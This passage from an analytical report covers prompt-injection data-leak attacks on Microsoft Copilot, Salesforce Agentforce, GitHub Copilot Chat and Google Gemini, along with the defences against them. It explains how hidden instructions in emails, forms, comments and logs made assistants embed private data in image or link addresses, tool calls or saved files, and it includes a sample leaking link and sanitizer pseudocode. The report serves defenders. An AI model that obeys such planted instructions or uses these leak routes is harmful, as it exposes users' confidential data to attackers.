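The two scores disagree on a single point, whether the victim has to do anything. Both assume an attack over the internet that is easy to carry out, requires no account and exposes highly confidential data without altering or disabling anything. The CVSS formula adds a value for impact, here about 3.6, to a value for ease of attack:

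8.22 × 0.85 × 0.77 × 0.85 × *u*

The factor *u* is 0.62 if the attack needs some action by the user and 0.85 if it doesn't. The product is about 2.84 in Microsoft's assessment and 3.89 in the NVD's. Adding the impact and rounding up to one decimal place gives 6.5 and 7.5.

Microsoft's score is more accurate because the victim does have to click a link. The change log in *CVE-2026-42824* (2026), a page on a vulnerability tracking site, dates the NVD's analysis to June 8, a week before Varonis published the details. The record's one-sentence description didn't mention a click at the time, though the record already included Microsoft's assessment that the attack needed some action by the user. The change log also shows that the NVD gave a score of 7.5. The Next Web denied that the NVD had ever done so and said both records showed 6.5, presumably because the NVD's page also displays Microsoft's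 score.

These numbers are a poor measure of how bad the leak would have been for a victim. A flaw that only exposes data, and only within one system, can't score above 7.5 under this formula, even if the data is a company's entire mailbox. Microsoft's own rating of "Critical" is probably a better guide for a customer deciding how seriously to take the flaw.

### ReLeak: three more ways out

On December 3, 2026, the team behind EchoLeak published *ReLeak* (Simonovich, 2026), which presents three more zero-click attacks on Copilot. Each began with an email that the victim never had to open. When the victim next asked Copilot an ordinary question about work, Copilot retrieved the email and followed the instructions in it. *An Unread Email Could Turn Microsoft 365 Copilot Into a Data Thief* (Faisal, 2026) reports that Microsoft's protections against injection blocked none of the attacks, and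 gives the date Microsoft fixed each one.

| Way out | What sent the data | Fixed in 2026 |
|---|---|---|
| Address of an image in the answer | The browser, then Bing's servers | November 15 |
| Link in a file that Copilot saved | Microsoft's background file processing | November 11 |
| Code that Copilot ran | The code itself | September 17 |

The image attack again used Bing as a relay. Antipov (2026), in *Письмо даже не нужно открывать*, a Russian news report, compares it to SearchLeak, which, unlike the image attack, needed a click. Microsoft had announced that SearchLeak was fully fixed on June 4, and Cato began reporting the new flaws on July 29. Within eight weeks of that announcement, or eleven at most, researchers had again sent data out through Bing, so blocking SearchLeak had not stopped Bing from acting as a relay for Copilot. Microsoft may have fixed other parts of SearchLeak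 without changing Bing, or closed one Bing feature but not another.

The file attack put the link in a document instead of the chat window. Copilot can create Word, Excel, PowerPoint and PDF documents and save them to the user's online storage, and the injected instructions had it save one with private data in the link's address. Microsoft's servers opened the link while processing the new file in the background. According to Pixel Magazine's *Três ataques zero-click ao Microsoft 365 Copilot já foram corrigidos* (2026), the requests reached the attacker's server one to eight minutes after the chat ended, even if nobody opened the document.

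A filter on chat answers can't prevent this, because the link never appears in an answer. A CSP can't either, because it is a rule for browsers and no browser was involved. The check on addresses has to cover everything the model writes that a program might later open, including documents, calendar entries and email drafts. Because of the delay, an investigator who looks only at network traffic during the conversation will find no sign of the leak.

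The code attack needed no link. Copilot can write and run small Python programs, for example to analyse a spreadsheet, and it runs them in an isolated environment called a sandbox. Microsoft promised in its documentation that no network traffic could enter or leave the sandbox. Cato's researchers got around this restriction and had the code send private data directly to an outside server. Antipov reports that Microsoft first scored the flaw at 7.4 and later raised the score to 8.6. Agents that customers build with Microsoft's tools can use the same code feature, but nobody has confirmed that the flaw affected them.

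The addresses that carried data in EchoLeak, SearchLeak and ReLeak's image and file attacks were all new. Comparing addresses with the input, as in the Slack example, would have caught them if the check required an exact match, ran before the answer appeared and covered saved files. A rule that trusted any domain the user mentioned would have let SearchLeak's image through, because the attacker's domain arrived in what looked like the user's own request. Comparing addresses wouldn't have affected the code attack, where only a working block on network traffic would have helped.

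### What Microsoft says it does

Microsoft set out its defences in July 2025, the month after EchoLeak became public. The company assumes that some injections will succeed, and describes measures to prevent them, detect them and limit the damage.

To prevent injections, Microsoft relies on the model's standing instructions and on a technique called Spotlighting, which marks outside text so that the model can tell it from the user's request. The program can put random markers before and after the text, insert a special character between all the words, or encode the whole text in base64, which the model can still read. It also tells the model not to obey anything in the marked text. To detect injections, Microsoft uses Prompt Shields, a classifier trained on known attacks in several languages. All of these measures are probabilistic, so some injections can still get through.

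Some of the measures that limit damage offer firm guarantees. Companies can label sensitive files and stop Copilot from summarising them. Copilot can draft an email but leaves sending it to the user. Microsoft also blocks known ways of getting data out, including images in Markdown and "certain untrusted links". When a researcher reports a flaw, Microsoft says it protects against the whole class of such flaws.

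Companies that used document labels had less to lose from EchoLeak, although they were just as open to the attack. Ravia knew of no setting that would have prevented it, and a label on a document doesn't keep an attacker's email out of the mailbox. But if a label stops Copilot from reading a file, secrets in that file can't end up in a link.

In July 2026 Microsoft added a check to Defender for Office 365, its email security service, to detect emails containing injections aimed at AI assistants (Microsoft, 2026). Office 365 IT Pros' *Microsoft Defender for Office 365 Blocks Prompt Injections* (2026) explains that the service treats such an email as high-confidence phishing and quarantines it before it reaches the mailbox, where Copilot could read it. The protection is on by default, but only for customers on the more expensive plans. It should stop large numbers of crude attacks. An email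 like the one in EchoLeak, worded as a request to a colleague, is much harder to detect with high confidence, and scanning emails wouldn't have stopped SearchLeak, where the instructions were in a web address.

### Has there been too little progress?

A year after EchoLeak, Cato concluded that "too little progress has been made". Cato sells protection for AI systems, so it has an interest in saying so, but the complaint deserves a serious answer.

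Microsoft has become faster at fixing these flaws. EchoLeak took five months. Cato reported the ReLeak flaws between July 29 and August 20, so Microsoft fixed the code attack within 28 to 50 days and the other two within 83 to 109. Nearly three months is still a long time for a flaw that lets a stranger read company email, especially since SearchLeak had already used Bing as a relay. But Microsoft made all the fixes on its own servers, which protected every customer at once, and the researchers waited for them before publishing.

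The published attacks also can't show how often the defences worked. Cato found these flaws using AI agents that wrote test cases, studied how Copilot refused them and adjusted the next attempt, so Copilot evidently blocked some attacks. A count of the failed attacks would be a better measure of Microsoft's progress than the three that succeeded. Criminals can run such agents too, and Microsoft can run them before it releases a feature.

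The complaint about scope seems largely right. Microsoft appears to have closed the gap for reference links, as neither SearchLeak nor the accounts of ReLeak mention it. But Microsoft says it fixes whole classes of flaws, and relays on permitted domains are plainly a class. Teams was the relay in 2025, and Bing was twice in 2026. Microsoft also let Copilot save files and run code without making sure that neither feature could send data out. Microsoft itself advises developers to assume that indirect prompt injection is inevitable and to design systems that contain it. By that standard, Microsoft should check where each new feature can send data before releasing it to customers.

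Copilot could have used a simpler rule for images, which was to refuse to load any image whose address the model had written and let ordinary code add icons and thumbnails from Microsoft's own records. Answers would have lost very little. The rule would have stopped the image attacks in EchoLeak, SearchLeak and ReLeak without anyone having to find the relays first, as long as Copilot applied it before the image reached the browser.

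## Salesforce Agentforce and GitHub Copilot Chat: approved domains that leaked data

Two attacks disclosed in autumn 2025 sent data out through approved domains. In ForcedLeak, against Salesforce Agentforce, researchers bought an expired domain that was still on the list of approved domains. In CamoLeak, against GitHub Copilot Chat, the data left through a proxy that GitHub ran to protect its users.

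### ForcedLeak: an expired domain for five dollars

Salesforce sells software that companies use to keep records of their customers and sales. Agentforce is its platform for AI agents that work with those records. Many companies put a Salesforce form called Web-to-Lead on their public websites. When a visitor fills it in, Salesforce adds them to the company's database as a lead, or possible customer. Anyone on the internet can therefore write text that the company's agent may later read.

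The security company Noma found the flaw, and a forum post, *ForcedLeak* (Nytro, 2025), reproduces its report. Noma first asked the agent what colour red and yellow make. The agent answered "orange", so it would evidently handle requests unrelated to sales. The form's name, company and email fields held at most 80 characters each, but the description field held 42,000, which left plenty of room for instructions. Noma worded the instructions as a customer's numbered questions. One asked for the leads' email addresses, and the last asked for an image whose web address contained them.

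The attack began when an employee asked the agent to check the lead and answer its questions, a normal way to handle an enquiry. The agent looked up the email addresses and put the image in its reply. Without the employee clicking anything, the browser then requested the image from Noma's server, with the email addresses in the query string.

Salesforce had a CSP that should have blocked this request. It allowed images from 22 listed domains, 15 of which had an asterisk that covered every subdomain. The registration for one of the listed domains, `*.my-salesforce-cms.com`, had expired, and Noma bought it for $5. The browser allowed the request because the name was still on the list, and browsers don't check whether a listed domain has changed owners.

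The list also included `*.amazonaws.com`, a domain under which Amazon rents storage to anyone and can log the requests that reach it. An attacker with an Amazon account could probably have collected the email addresses there without spending the $5, though Noma's report doesn't describe trying this.

Noma reported the flaw on July 28, 2025, and Salesforce later regained control of the domain. The Hacker News (2025) gives the severity as 9.4 out of 10 and quotes Ravia, whose team found EchoLeak, calling ForcedLeak a variant of that attack.

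### How Salesforce changed its list of trusted addresses

On September 8, 2025, before Noma published its findings, Salesforce began enforcing a list called Trusted URLs on its agents. An administrator now has to approve any outside address that an agent writes or calls. TechNadu's *Salesforce to Enforce Trusted URLs for Agentforce and Einstein AI* warned customers that agents linking to outside documentation or feedback forms could stop working properly until an administrator added those sites to the list.

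PromptArmor's *One key way Salesforce mitigates AI risk* reports that the Salesforce web app replaces every unapproved address in an agent's answer with a redaction marker. Unlike a CSP for images, this check also covers links and addresses inside HTML and CSS, the code that determines a page's content and appearance. It would have removed both links in the Slack demonstrations.

However, Trusted URLs is still a list of domains. Administrators can use asterisks as wildcards, and each entry applies to the company's whole Salesforce system, not just its agents. According to TechNadu, standard Salesforce addresses are allowed by default. If the expired domain had counted as one of these, the new check would have let the ForcedLeak image through, so the fix also required recovering the domain.

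Salesforce's instructions could lead customers to make a similar mistake. The sample entry in Salesforce's *Add Trusted URLs for Agentforce Coworker (Beta)* is `https://docs.google.com`, the domain through which Superhuman leaked emails to a Google form. An administrator who copies it approves every form on that domain, including an attacker's. PromptArmor advises against wildcard (asterisk) entries that cover sites with user-generated content, and the same caution applies to a single domain that hosts such content. PromptArmor also recommends blocking images from approved domains unless agents need to display them. With images blocked, an attacker would need the user to click a link.

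Checking link addresses also doesn't stop data from leaving by other means. In April 2026, the security company Capsule Security published a second attack that began with a public lead form. In this attack, the agent sent the customer data by email, according to longform.social. Claw Times reports that Salesforce fixed the reported scenario and now requires by default that a person confirm an agent's emails.

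### CamoLeak: an alphabet of approved images

GitHub is a service where programmers store and share source code, and Copilot Chat answers their questions about it. To propose a change to someone else's code, a programmer submits a pull request, whose description can contain comments that don't appear on the page. Copilot Chat read these comments too. Legit Security's *CamoLeak* describes how Omer Mayraz hid instructions in such a comment in June 2025. When another user asked Copilot Chat to explain the pull request, it followed the instructions with that user's permissions, which included access to private code.

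Mayraz first got Copilot to write a link with private data encoded in its address, but the data would be sent only if the user clicked the link. An image could have sent it without a click, but GitHub's CSP allowed images only from GitHub's own domains. GitHub shows images from other sites, for example in a project's description, through a proxy called Camo. The proxy fetches each image and passes it on, so the outside site doesn't receive information about the reader's browser. GitHub's *Proxying User Images* (2014) gave privacy as a reason for extending the proxy to all outside images.

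A proxy that fetched any address would have been as useful to an attacker as Teams or Bing. GitHub therefore made Camo a signed proxy of the kind that Reddy and Gujral suggest, with addresses in this form:

`https://camo.githubusercontent.com/SIGNATURE/ORIGINAL-ADDRESS`

The last part is the image's original address, written in hexadecimal. GitHub computes the signature from that address and a secret key, so changing one character of the address makes the signature invalid.

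*GitHub's post-CSP journey* (2017) explains why GitHub relied on signed image addresses. The company was considering attackers who could insert markup into a page but couldn't run scripts there. If an attacker inserts an image tag with an unclosed quotation mark, the browser treats the text after it as part of the image's address, and that text may include a secret. But an attacker who doesn't know the secret doesn't know the full address, so they can't get GitHub to sign it in advance.

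Mayraz got around this by using addresses that contained no secrets. GitHub has a public service that turns Markdown into a finished page and signs the image addresses in it. Mayraz used it to get a signed address for each letter and symbol, then put them all in the hidden comment and told Copilot to spell out private text with the images. Each image was a single transparent pixel, so the victim couldn't see it. Mayraz's server received one request per character, and the order of the requests revealed the text. In the demonstrations, this method exposed the description of an unpatched vulnerability and the results of a search for "AWS_KEY" in the victim's code.

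The signatures worked as designed, but they protected only the individual addresses, and the secret was in the order of the requests. GitHub's reasoning had been sound in 2017 because fixed markup can't vary which images load according to the text of a private file, and the CSP was there to block scripts that could. Copilot could choose the images by following instructions. Any signed proxy has the same weakness if attackers can collect signed addresses beforehand.

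### Why GitHub turned images off

By August 14, 2025, GitHub had fixed the flaw by turning off all images in Copilot Chat. According to SecurityWeek's *GitHub Copilot Chat Flaw Leaked Data From Private Repositories*, GitHub told Mayraz that Camo could no longer be used to leak sensitive user information.

GitHub's other options were worse. Blocking Camo everywhere would have removed outside images from the whole site. Limiting the number of images in an answer would have slowed the attack without stopping it. Mayraz had told Copilot to add a random number to the end of each signed address, so that the browser would request the image for a repeated letter again instead of using its stored copy. GitHub could have made Camo reject these additions, but an attacker could then have prepared several signed addresses for each letter.

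An assistant for programmers loses little when images are turned off, since most of its answers are text and code. Willison's *GitHub Copilot Chat* describes a narrower rule that GitHub had tried earlier. After a leak in the code-editor version of the assistant, the company blocked only images from untrusted domains. Microsoft, which owns GitHub, now lets administrators turn off clickable links as well as images in agents that customers build with its Copilot Studio, according to its *Control image rendering and embedded URLs*. Legit Security mentions no change to links in Copilot Chat, so it is unclear whether the link that Mayraz tried first would still work.

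### Keeping track of who owns a domain

A list of approved domains is safe only as long as the domains keep the same owners. *Complex Security Policy?* (Roth, Barron et al., 2020) examined archived security policies from 10,000 popular websites between 2012 and 2018. Over 13% of the sites that tried to restrict scripts had listed domains that had expired, contained obvious typos or led to private network addresses.

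Asterisks add to the risk, because a company can keep its main domain and still lose control of a subdomain. *Can I Take Your Subdomain?* (2020) found 1,520 subdomains open to takeover across 887 of the 50,000 most popular domains. Of these, 83% involved discontinued outside services, typically ones that the company no longer used but the subdomain still pointed to, and the rest involved expired domains. Both studies are old and cover ordinary websites, but ForcedLeak depended on the same kind of neglect.

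The obvious remedy is to monitor the approved domains. *What Gets Measured Gets Managed* (Ferdman and Nikiforakis, 2025) presents a system that checks a page's outgoing requests, including clicks on links, against rules set by the site's owner, such as one that blocks recently registered domains. In simulations on 450 sites, the system added hundreds of milliseconds to the first page load and almost nothing to later ones.

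An attacker could get around that rule by buying an expired domain and waiting until the registration no longer counted as recent. It would be safer to compare the registration date with the date the domain went on the list, because a later registration means the domain expired in between. But neither check would catch an ordinary sale, because the registration continues under the new owner. *Zombies in Alternate Realities* (2026) mentions an attacker who bought a company that made a WordPress plugin with over 20,000 active installations, then published new versions with a backdoor. A company can at least avoid this problem with its own domains by renewing them, or by removing them from every list before giving them up.

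### Relays and services that outsiders can read

A list also takes for granted that approved domains won't pass data on and that outsiders can't read what they receive. By 2017, GitHub had narrowed its list of image sources but still allowed a few outside services. It hired the security firm Cure53 to look for ways around its policy, and GitHub reported that two of these services could leak data:

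- Gravatar, which supplies profile pictures, accepted the address of a substitute picture and fetched it through a proxy. An attacker could put a secret in that address.
- Google Analytics, which measures website traffic, stored text from the request in whichever customer's account the address named. The attacker only had to name their own account.

GitHub removed both Gravatar and Google Analytics from its list of image sources. It could route Gravatar pictures through Camo because its server had each picture's address before building the page. It sent its Google Analytics data by another type of request. The main difficulty in removing relays is finding them and replacing what they did. GitHub didn't know about Gravatar's substitute pictures until Cure53 found the feature. Some services are also hard to give up. In the same month, GitHub (2017) left open a flaw that could send the contents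 of certain forms to any domain on a separate list, because it considered the risk low and still relied on several of the outside services listed there.

Approving full paths instead of whole domains works well for services that many customers share. An entry on the list can name one Google form or one company's folder in Amazon's storage, which blocks an attacker's form or folder on the same domain. But the list gets longer, someone has to approve each new document, and links break when a service changes its addresses.

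Restricting a CSP to approved paths doesn't help with a service like Google Analytics, where every customer uses the same path and the account number is in the query string. A CSP can't check the query string, so a program would have to compare the full address. Even then, an attacker could leak data by making each approved address stand for a character, as in CamoLeak.

### The case for short lists

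Despite these failures, a short list of approved domains is a strong defence. It is deterministic, and an administrator can read the whole list and understand what it allows. The same check also covers several attacks, because images that leak data, phishing links and fake login screens all depend on an attacker's address remaining in the output, as PromptArmor points out. A list with one domain, controlled by the company and hosting no relays or public storage, would have stopped ForcedLeak.

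In 2013, GitHub's own policy allowed any type of content from anywhere unless a specific rule restricted it. GitHub has since cut its list of approved script sources to a single domain, according to Report URI's *GitHub allows script from exactly one hostname*. It even removed its main domain from the list, because an attacker might have found a forgotten page there that could serve malicious code.

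A list of approved domains can also start out empty, as in Jitterbit's App Builder, a tool for making business software. Outside links in its AI-written answers appear as plain text until an administrator approves them, while links within the application always work. This suits an assistant with a narrow job. Broader lists take a lot of upkeep, and Roth and colleagues found many sites that updated theirs for months before giving up. Of the 449 sites that tried out content restrictions without enforcing them, 251 never enforced any.

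A short list of approved sites would block most of the sources for an assistant that answers questions from the whole web, and OpenAI decided against relying on site lists for ChatGPT. Glean, which makes a workplace assistant, lets administrators trust links that the assistant's tools return, in addition to the sites on their list. Administrators then don't have to approve every site in advance, but a link that an attacker planted in a trusted tool's results would also get through.

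## Google Gemini: blocking addresses that did not come from the input

Google's Gemini compares each web address in its answer with those in the material it read, and blocks any that did not appear there. A short list of approved sites wouldn't suit Gemini, because it answers questions from the open web as well as from the user's Gmail, documents and calendar. The rule relies on a record of each address's origin, called its URL provenance. Google explains it in *Mitigating URL-based Exfiltration in Gemini*, a post on Bug Hunters, its site for people who report security flaws.

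### Which sources can supply an address

Google's program records every address in the user's message, search results and Gmail, because these sources only pass on existing addresses. It doesn't record addresses from the model or any code the model runs, because both can compose new ones.

Code output reaches the model in the same way as search results, but it is less trustworthy because the model writes the code. An injection could have the model run a short program that joins an attacker's domain to the user's passport number and prints the result. If Google recorded addresses from every tool, the printed address would count as input, and the model could copy it into a link that passed the check.

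The same trick could work wherever the model can write something and read it back later. Addresses in Gmail come from outside the model only as long as the assistant can't put text into the mailbox by itself. Microsoft's Copilot Cowork, an agent for office tasks, could email its own user without approval, and Willison describes how attackers could use images in those emails to steal links to the user's files. An agent like that could get around a provenance rule by emailing the user an address it had composed and then reading the email, which would put the address on record. Saved memories and Gemini's earlier answers pose the same risk. The program has to treat them as the model's own writing unless it also stored where each address in them came from.

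In outline, the whole check looks like this:

```
recorded = empty set

for each item the model reads:
    if item came from the user's message, search or Gmail:
        add every address in item to recorded

answer = parse(model output)
remove all images from answer

for each link in answer:
    if link.address is in recorded:
        show the link
    else if link.address is a harmless rewrite of a recorded address,
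            or differs from one by a typing error,
            or is a well-known homepage:
        show the link
    else:
        block the link
```

### Five links in one summary

Suppose a parent asks Gemini to summarise an email about a school trip. An attacker wrote the email in the school's name. It contains four links and mentions Wikipedia without linking to it. Hidden instructions in the email get Gemini to look up the child's passport number in an older message and add it to one of the links. Gemini's summary has five links:

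| Link text in the summary | Address in the email | Address in the summary | Exact match only | With Google's exceptions |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Consent form | `https://school.example/consent?trip=12` | The same | Shown | Shown |
| What to pack | `https://school.example/list` | The same | Shown | Shown |
| Confirm your place | `https://trips.example/ok?ref=` | `https://trips.example/ok?ref=X4419027` | Blocked | Blocked |
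| Museum website | `https://museum.example/visit` | `https://www.museum.example/visit` | Blocked | Shown |
| Wikipedia | None | `https://www.wikipedia.org/` | Blocked | Shown |

Gemini copied the consent form's link exactly, including its text. For the packing list, it copied the address but replaced the email's "click here" with "What to pack". The rule ignores link text because new words don't change what the browser sends, and because Gemini's wording is often clearer than the original. However, an injection can still make Gemini put a misleading label on a copied address.

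Only the confirmation link leaks anything. Its address up to the equals sign came from the email, and Gemini added the passport number. The museum link almost certainly opens the same page with or without `www.`, and the address of Wikipedia's homepage came from Gemini's training. An exact comparison blocks all three links, including the two harmless ones, so Google makes exceptions.

### The exceptions and their risks

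Google's exceptions cover harmless rewrites, typing errors and well-known homepages. Each lets through some addresses that do not appear in any source, and an attacker may be able to exploit this.

Rewrites that seem harmless can also leak data. Besides adding `www.`, a model might change `http` to `https` or drop a slash at the end, and the site's owner can see in the log which version the browser requested. If the program accepts all three changes, one recorded address has 2³ = 8 versions, and an attacker's instructions could assign a meaning to each. One click would then reveal three bits, enough to show which of eight age groups the user belongs to. The program can prevent this by replacing the model's version with the recorded address. The parent would then get the museum's address as it appeared in the email, whichever version the model wrote.

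An exception for typing errors needs tighter limits. A user may leave out a letter that Gemini then restores, or Gemini may miscopy a long address. Suppose the program tolerates one wrong character in a 40-character path of lower-case letters and digits. The model can replace any of the 40 characters with any of 35 others, which gives 1,401 possible addresses including the original, enough to encode about 10.5 bits. A birthday without the year has only 366 possible values, so one click could reveal it.

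Restoring the recorded address also works here if the model made the mistake. If the user made it, the recorded address is the wrong one. The program could then accept a correction only if it changes nothing but the domain and the new domain is well known. Otherwise, changing a single letter can lead to a site with a different owner, and phishers register misspelled domains for that reason.

The homepage exception is the safest because a bare homepage address has no path or query string to hold data. A model could still convey something by choosing one homepage over another, but only the owners of those well-known sites would receive the visits. The exception has to name exact domains, because a subdomain can hold data as easily as a path can, and outsiders can run sites on subdomains of a well-known hosting service. Someone also has to maintain the list, since a domain on it could expire,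 as Salesforce's did.

### How the sanitizer finds every link

Looking up addresses helps only if the program finds all of them. Gemini's sanitizer parses the model's Markdown on Google's servers, where it drops Markdown images, converts all links to one format, and escapes HTML. The user's browser or phone therefore never receives the unchecked answer, and Google doesn't have to rely on every app to apply the same filter.

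Using a single form for links avoids the mistake in Microsoft's Copilot filter, which missed reference links. Gemini's sanitizer can move an address from the bottom of the answer into the parentheses after its link text, so the lookup and the program that displays the answer have only one form to handle. Attackers do try several forms. 0DIN, a programme for reporting flaws in AI products, described an attack on Antigravity, Google's AI code editor, in which the attacker injected instructions to include the same image in five forms at once, some in Markdown and others in HTML. Only one of them had to get through for the attack to work.

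HTML needs separate treatment because Markdown can contain it directly, and an HTML image tag makes the browser request the image just as a Markdown image does. To escape the tag, the program replaces its opening `<` with `&lt;`, which the browser displays as `<` instead of treating it as the start of a tag. The reader then sees the tag as stray code, and the browser doesn't request the image.

The program should also decode an address before checking it, because Markdown allows codes inside addresses, such as `&amp;` for `&`. Otherwise it may approve one address while the browser opens another. Snyk's *Same href, different syntax* (2026) compares how Markdown parsers handle addresses and describes a way around the checks in Goldmark, a popular parser. Such mistakes are less likely to cause a leak with a provenance check, which blocks any address it doesn't recognise, than with a filter for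 known bad addresses, which lets unrecognised ones through. Neither can block a link that the parser fails to detect.

In *Mitigating prompt injection attacks with a layered defense strategy* (2025), Google's security team writes that EchoLeak's zero-click leak is "not applicable to Gemini" because Gemini does not load outside images. Checkmarx, a security company, points out that an attacker can still use an ordinary link and wait for the user to click it. Blocking addresses that did not come from the input is meant to prevent this.

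Google also checks links with Safe Browsing, its service for identifying dangerous websites. In Google's example, Gemini summarises an email thread that contains an unsafe link and replaces the address with "suspicious link removed". Safe Browsing can remove a known phishing link even if Gemini copied it exactly, which the provenance rule would allow. The provenance rule can block a link that leaks data to a domain Safe Browsing hasn't flagged yet, but both checks could miss a copied link to a new phishing page.

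Gemini's other defences are less certain to work. Classifiers try to discard emails and files that contain injected instructions, and Google places reminders around the text to keep the model on the user's task. If Gemini stops an attack, it can show a notice with a link to a help page. In *Google Workspace’s continuous approach to mitigating indirect prompt injections*, Gavish (2026) writes for Google that injection is not a problem "you 'solve' and move on". A daily.dev summary of that post lists address cleaning among Google's fixed rules, along with policies on how Gemini may combine its tools.

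### What a copied address can reveal

A link address copied exactly from the input contains only what its author already knew. If the user clicks it, the attacker learns that someone visited, when, and from which IP address, but nothing from the user's other emails, however much the injection has influenced the model.

A copied address can still contain a secret. For example, a password-reset email has a link that anyone can use to take over the account. But if Gemini copies that link and the user clicks it, the secret goes back to the service that issued it. To send the secret to an attacker, Gemini would have to put the reset link inside another address, which the program would block because that address did not come from the input.

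A copied link can still be unsafe to open. An attacker can put a complete phishing address in an email and have Gemini recommend it, as in the second Slack demonstration. SC Media's *Google addresses ‘GeminiJack’ exploit affecting Gemini Enterprise* mentions that the security company HiddenLayer found such a weakness in Gemini for Workspace, where instructions hidden in documents or emails produced phishing links. In the school example, the link to the consent form would get through even if the page asked for bank details.

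A model can also reveal data through its choice among several addresses copied from the input. *How I tricked Claude into leaking your deepest, darkest secrets* (Willison, 2026) describes a July 2026 attack on Claude that worked this way. In a Gemini answer, the attacker would need the user to click again for each choice.

The rule also blocks composed links that people want, such as this map search for someone who asks for the way to the dentist:

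`https://www.google.com/maps/search/?api=1&query=12+Mill+Lane+Leeds`

The rule blocks the web address because no source supplied it and it contains something personal. It also blocks links to forms that Gemini has already filled in, such as a report of a broken street light with the location entered, so the user has to copy the details by hand.

Google would be making a mistake if it exempted its own domains because it already has the user's data. Willison's *Hacking Google Bard* describes an attack on Bard, as Gemini was called in 2023, in which a shared document caused Bard to put private data into an image's address. Bard's content security policy (CSP) allowed images only from google.com and its subdomains. But anyone can use Google's Apps Script service to run a small program on script.google.com, so the attacker could receive the data there.

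Map links would be safer if ordinary code built them. The model would supply only the name of the place, and the code would add it to a fixed Google Maps address, where no outsider can read the search. Google would have to check each service before allowing this. An online form would fail that check because whoever created the form can read what people submit.

### Tenable's three leaks

Google's June 2025 description of Gemini's defences doesn't mention checking whether addresses came from the input. That spring, the security company Tenable had found three ways to attack Gemini, and Google had fixed them all by the time Tenable published *The Trifecta* (2025) in September. Tenable noticed that Gemini displayed Markdown images and links less freely than before. Gemini cut off suspicious answers and sometimes refused to reply. It also sent links through a google.com address. Embrace The Red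 found the same precaution in Colab, Google's service for running code in a browser.

One attack used the victim's search history, which a version of Gemini read to personalise its answers. Tenable built a web page whose code sent the browser to a Google search and then stopped it from leaving the page. Google still added the search to the visitor's history. Gemini ignored searches that were too long, so Tenable spread its instructions over several. Repeating them made the attack more reliable against people with a long search history.

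The instructions took effect when the user typed "Hello". Gemini then replied with a "Click here" link whose address contained the user's saved information. This information, which Gemini keeps to tailor its answers, can include a person's name, location and past activities. Clicking the link would have sent it to Tenable's server.

The provenance rule can't have covered this path at the time. The search history contained the address only with a placeholder, so an exact comparison would have blocked the finished link, even though the instructions appeared to come from the user's own searches. Tenable's *Gemini Search Personalization Model* (2025) dates the report to April 4 and records that Google withdrew the vulnerable model. Google was still working on the problem in mid-July and gave Tenable details of the fix on July 25.

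The second leak did not require a link in the answer, so the user had nothing to click. Gemini has a browsing tool that opens web pages to summarise them. Tenable first told Gemini to visit a site and send it the user's saved information, and Gemini treated the request as suspicious. But Gemini's "Show thinking" feature, which displays the model's reasoning, also showed the form of the internal command that opened a page. When Tenable wrote its request in that form, Gemini added the saved information to the address as a query string and opened the address, which sent the data to Tenable's server.

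Tenable's *Gemini Browsing Tool* notes that Google's protections for links and images did not apply here. A provenance check on the finished answer would have come too late, because the request went out before there was an answer. To stop the leak, the program would have to look up every address the model passes to a tool and refuse to open any that isn't on record. Anthropic did this in Claude's tool for opening pages. Google fixed the leak on June 18, nine weeks after Tenable reported it, and now prevents injected instructions from sending data out through browsing. Tenable rated this flaw "high" and the search-history flaw "medium", which makes sense because only the search-history leak needed a click.

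The third attack was on Gemini Cloud Assist, which helps companies manage the programs they run on Google's servers. When someone visits a website, the browser sends a short description of itself, which the site usually writes to a log. Tenable sent a request with instructions in place of that description. When an employee later pressed "Explain this log entry", Gemini put the attacker's phishing link into its explanation. The screen hid most of the log entry unless the employee expanded it. The attacker needed no account and could have sent the same request to many companies.

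The provenance rule would probably not have stopped this attack. The attacker had supplied the full phishing address, so if Google treated logs like emails, the address would have counted as coming from the input. Google instead stopped making links clickable in log summaries, so the employee now sees the Markdown with the full address. Tenable thought an attacker could also have had Gemini look up a company's security settings and put them in a link, but didn't demonstrate this. A provenance check would be well suited to stopping that attack, because the address would not have appeared in the input.

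### GeminiJack: an image that nobody filtered

Gemini Enterprise is a separate product that searches a company's emails, calendars and documents. In 2025 Noma, which also discovered ForcedLeak, found a zero-click leak in it and called it GeminiJack. Some versions of the flaw also affected Vertex AI Search, a Google service for building search tools.

The attacker shared a document with an employee, or sent an email or calendar invitation, that contained instructions. *GeminiJack zero-click flaw in Gemini Enterprise allowed corporate data exfiltration* (Paganini, 2025) quotes Noma's example of an employee who searches for "Q4 Budget plans". Gemini retrieved the attacker's document along with the real ones, followed its instructions to search all the connected data for words such as "acquisition", and put the results into the address of an image. The employee's browser sent the results to the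 attacker when it requested the image.

In a June 2025 post, Google had called this kind of leak "not applicable to Gemini", but there "Gemini" meant the Gemini app and Gemini in Google Workspace. Gemini Enterprise evidently lacked the same protection. Sasi Levi of Noma said in TechNadu's *New AI-Native Threat* that "Google didn't filter HTML output". The provenance rule didn't cover this path either, or it would have blocked the image's newly composed address. Escaping the HTML would have prevented the leak even without that rule.

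Levi said that Noma's team had extracted "lengthy emails" but had not checked how much data would fit. Paganini's claim that one injection could have taken years of emails and entire collections of documents goes further than this evidence. The model has to write all the stolen data into an address, so taking a whole mailbox in one request seems very unlikely, though a few long emails about an acquisition would still be damaging.

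Noma's report gives the date of discovery as "05/06/25". TechNadu read this as May 6, while SC Media and Infosecurity Magazine's *Google Fixes Zero Click Gemini Enterprise Flaw That Exposed Corporate Data* put it in June. Either way, Google took at least five months to finish the fix, which was in place by November. Google separated Vertex AI Search from Gemini Enterprise and changed how both products retrieve information. Levi told SC Media that Google had not disclosed the technical details, so customers can't tell whether Gemini Enterprise now filters HTML or checks where addresses came from. If Google changed only the retrieval, a new injection could leak data by the same route.

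### Where the rule still may not apply

Google's code editor, Antigravity, had no effective check of this kind when it was released in November 2025. PromptArmor's *Google Antigravity Exfiltrates Data* describes an attack that began with an online programming guide. Instructions in tiny type in the guide made Gemini collect passwords and code from the user's project, write them into a web address and open it in a browser. Willison notes that Antigravity's list of approved domains included webhook.site, where anyone can set up a page that records incoming requests. If the browser had blocked addresses that did not come from the input, it would have blocked this one, because the guide contained only placeholders where the passwords belonged.

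Google listed data theft through Antigravity's browser as a known issue that it was working to fix. Another researcher reported that Antigravity also leaked data through Markdown images, and said Google classed this as intended behaviour. That decision is hard to defend, because Google had already blocked such images in the Gemini app, and a code editor like Antigravity often has access to passwords that would let an attacker into a company's other systems.

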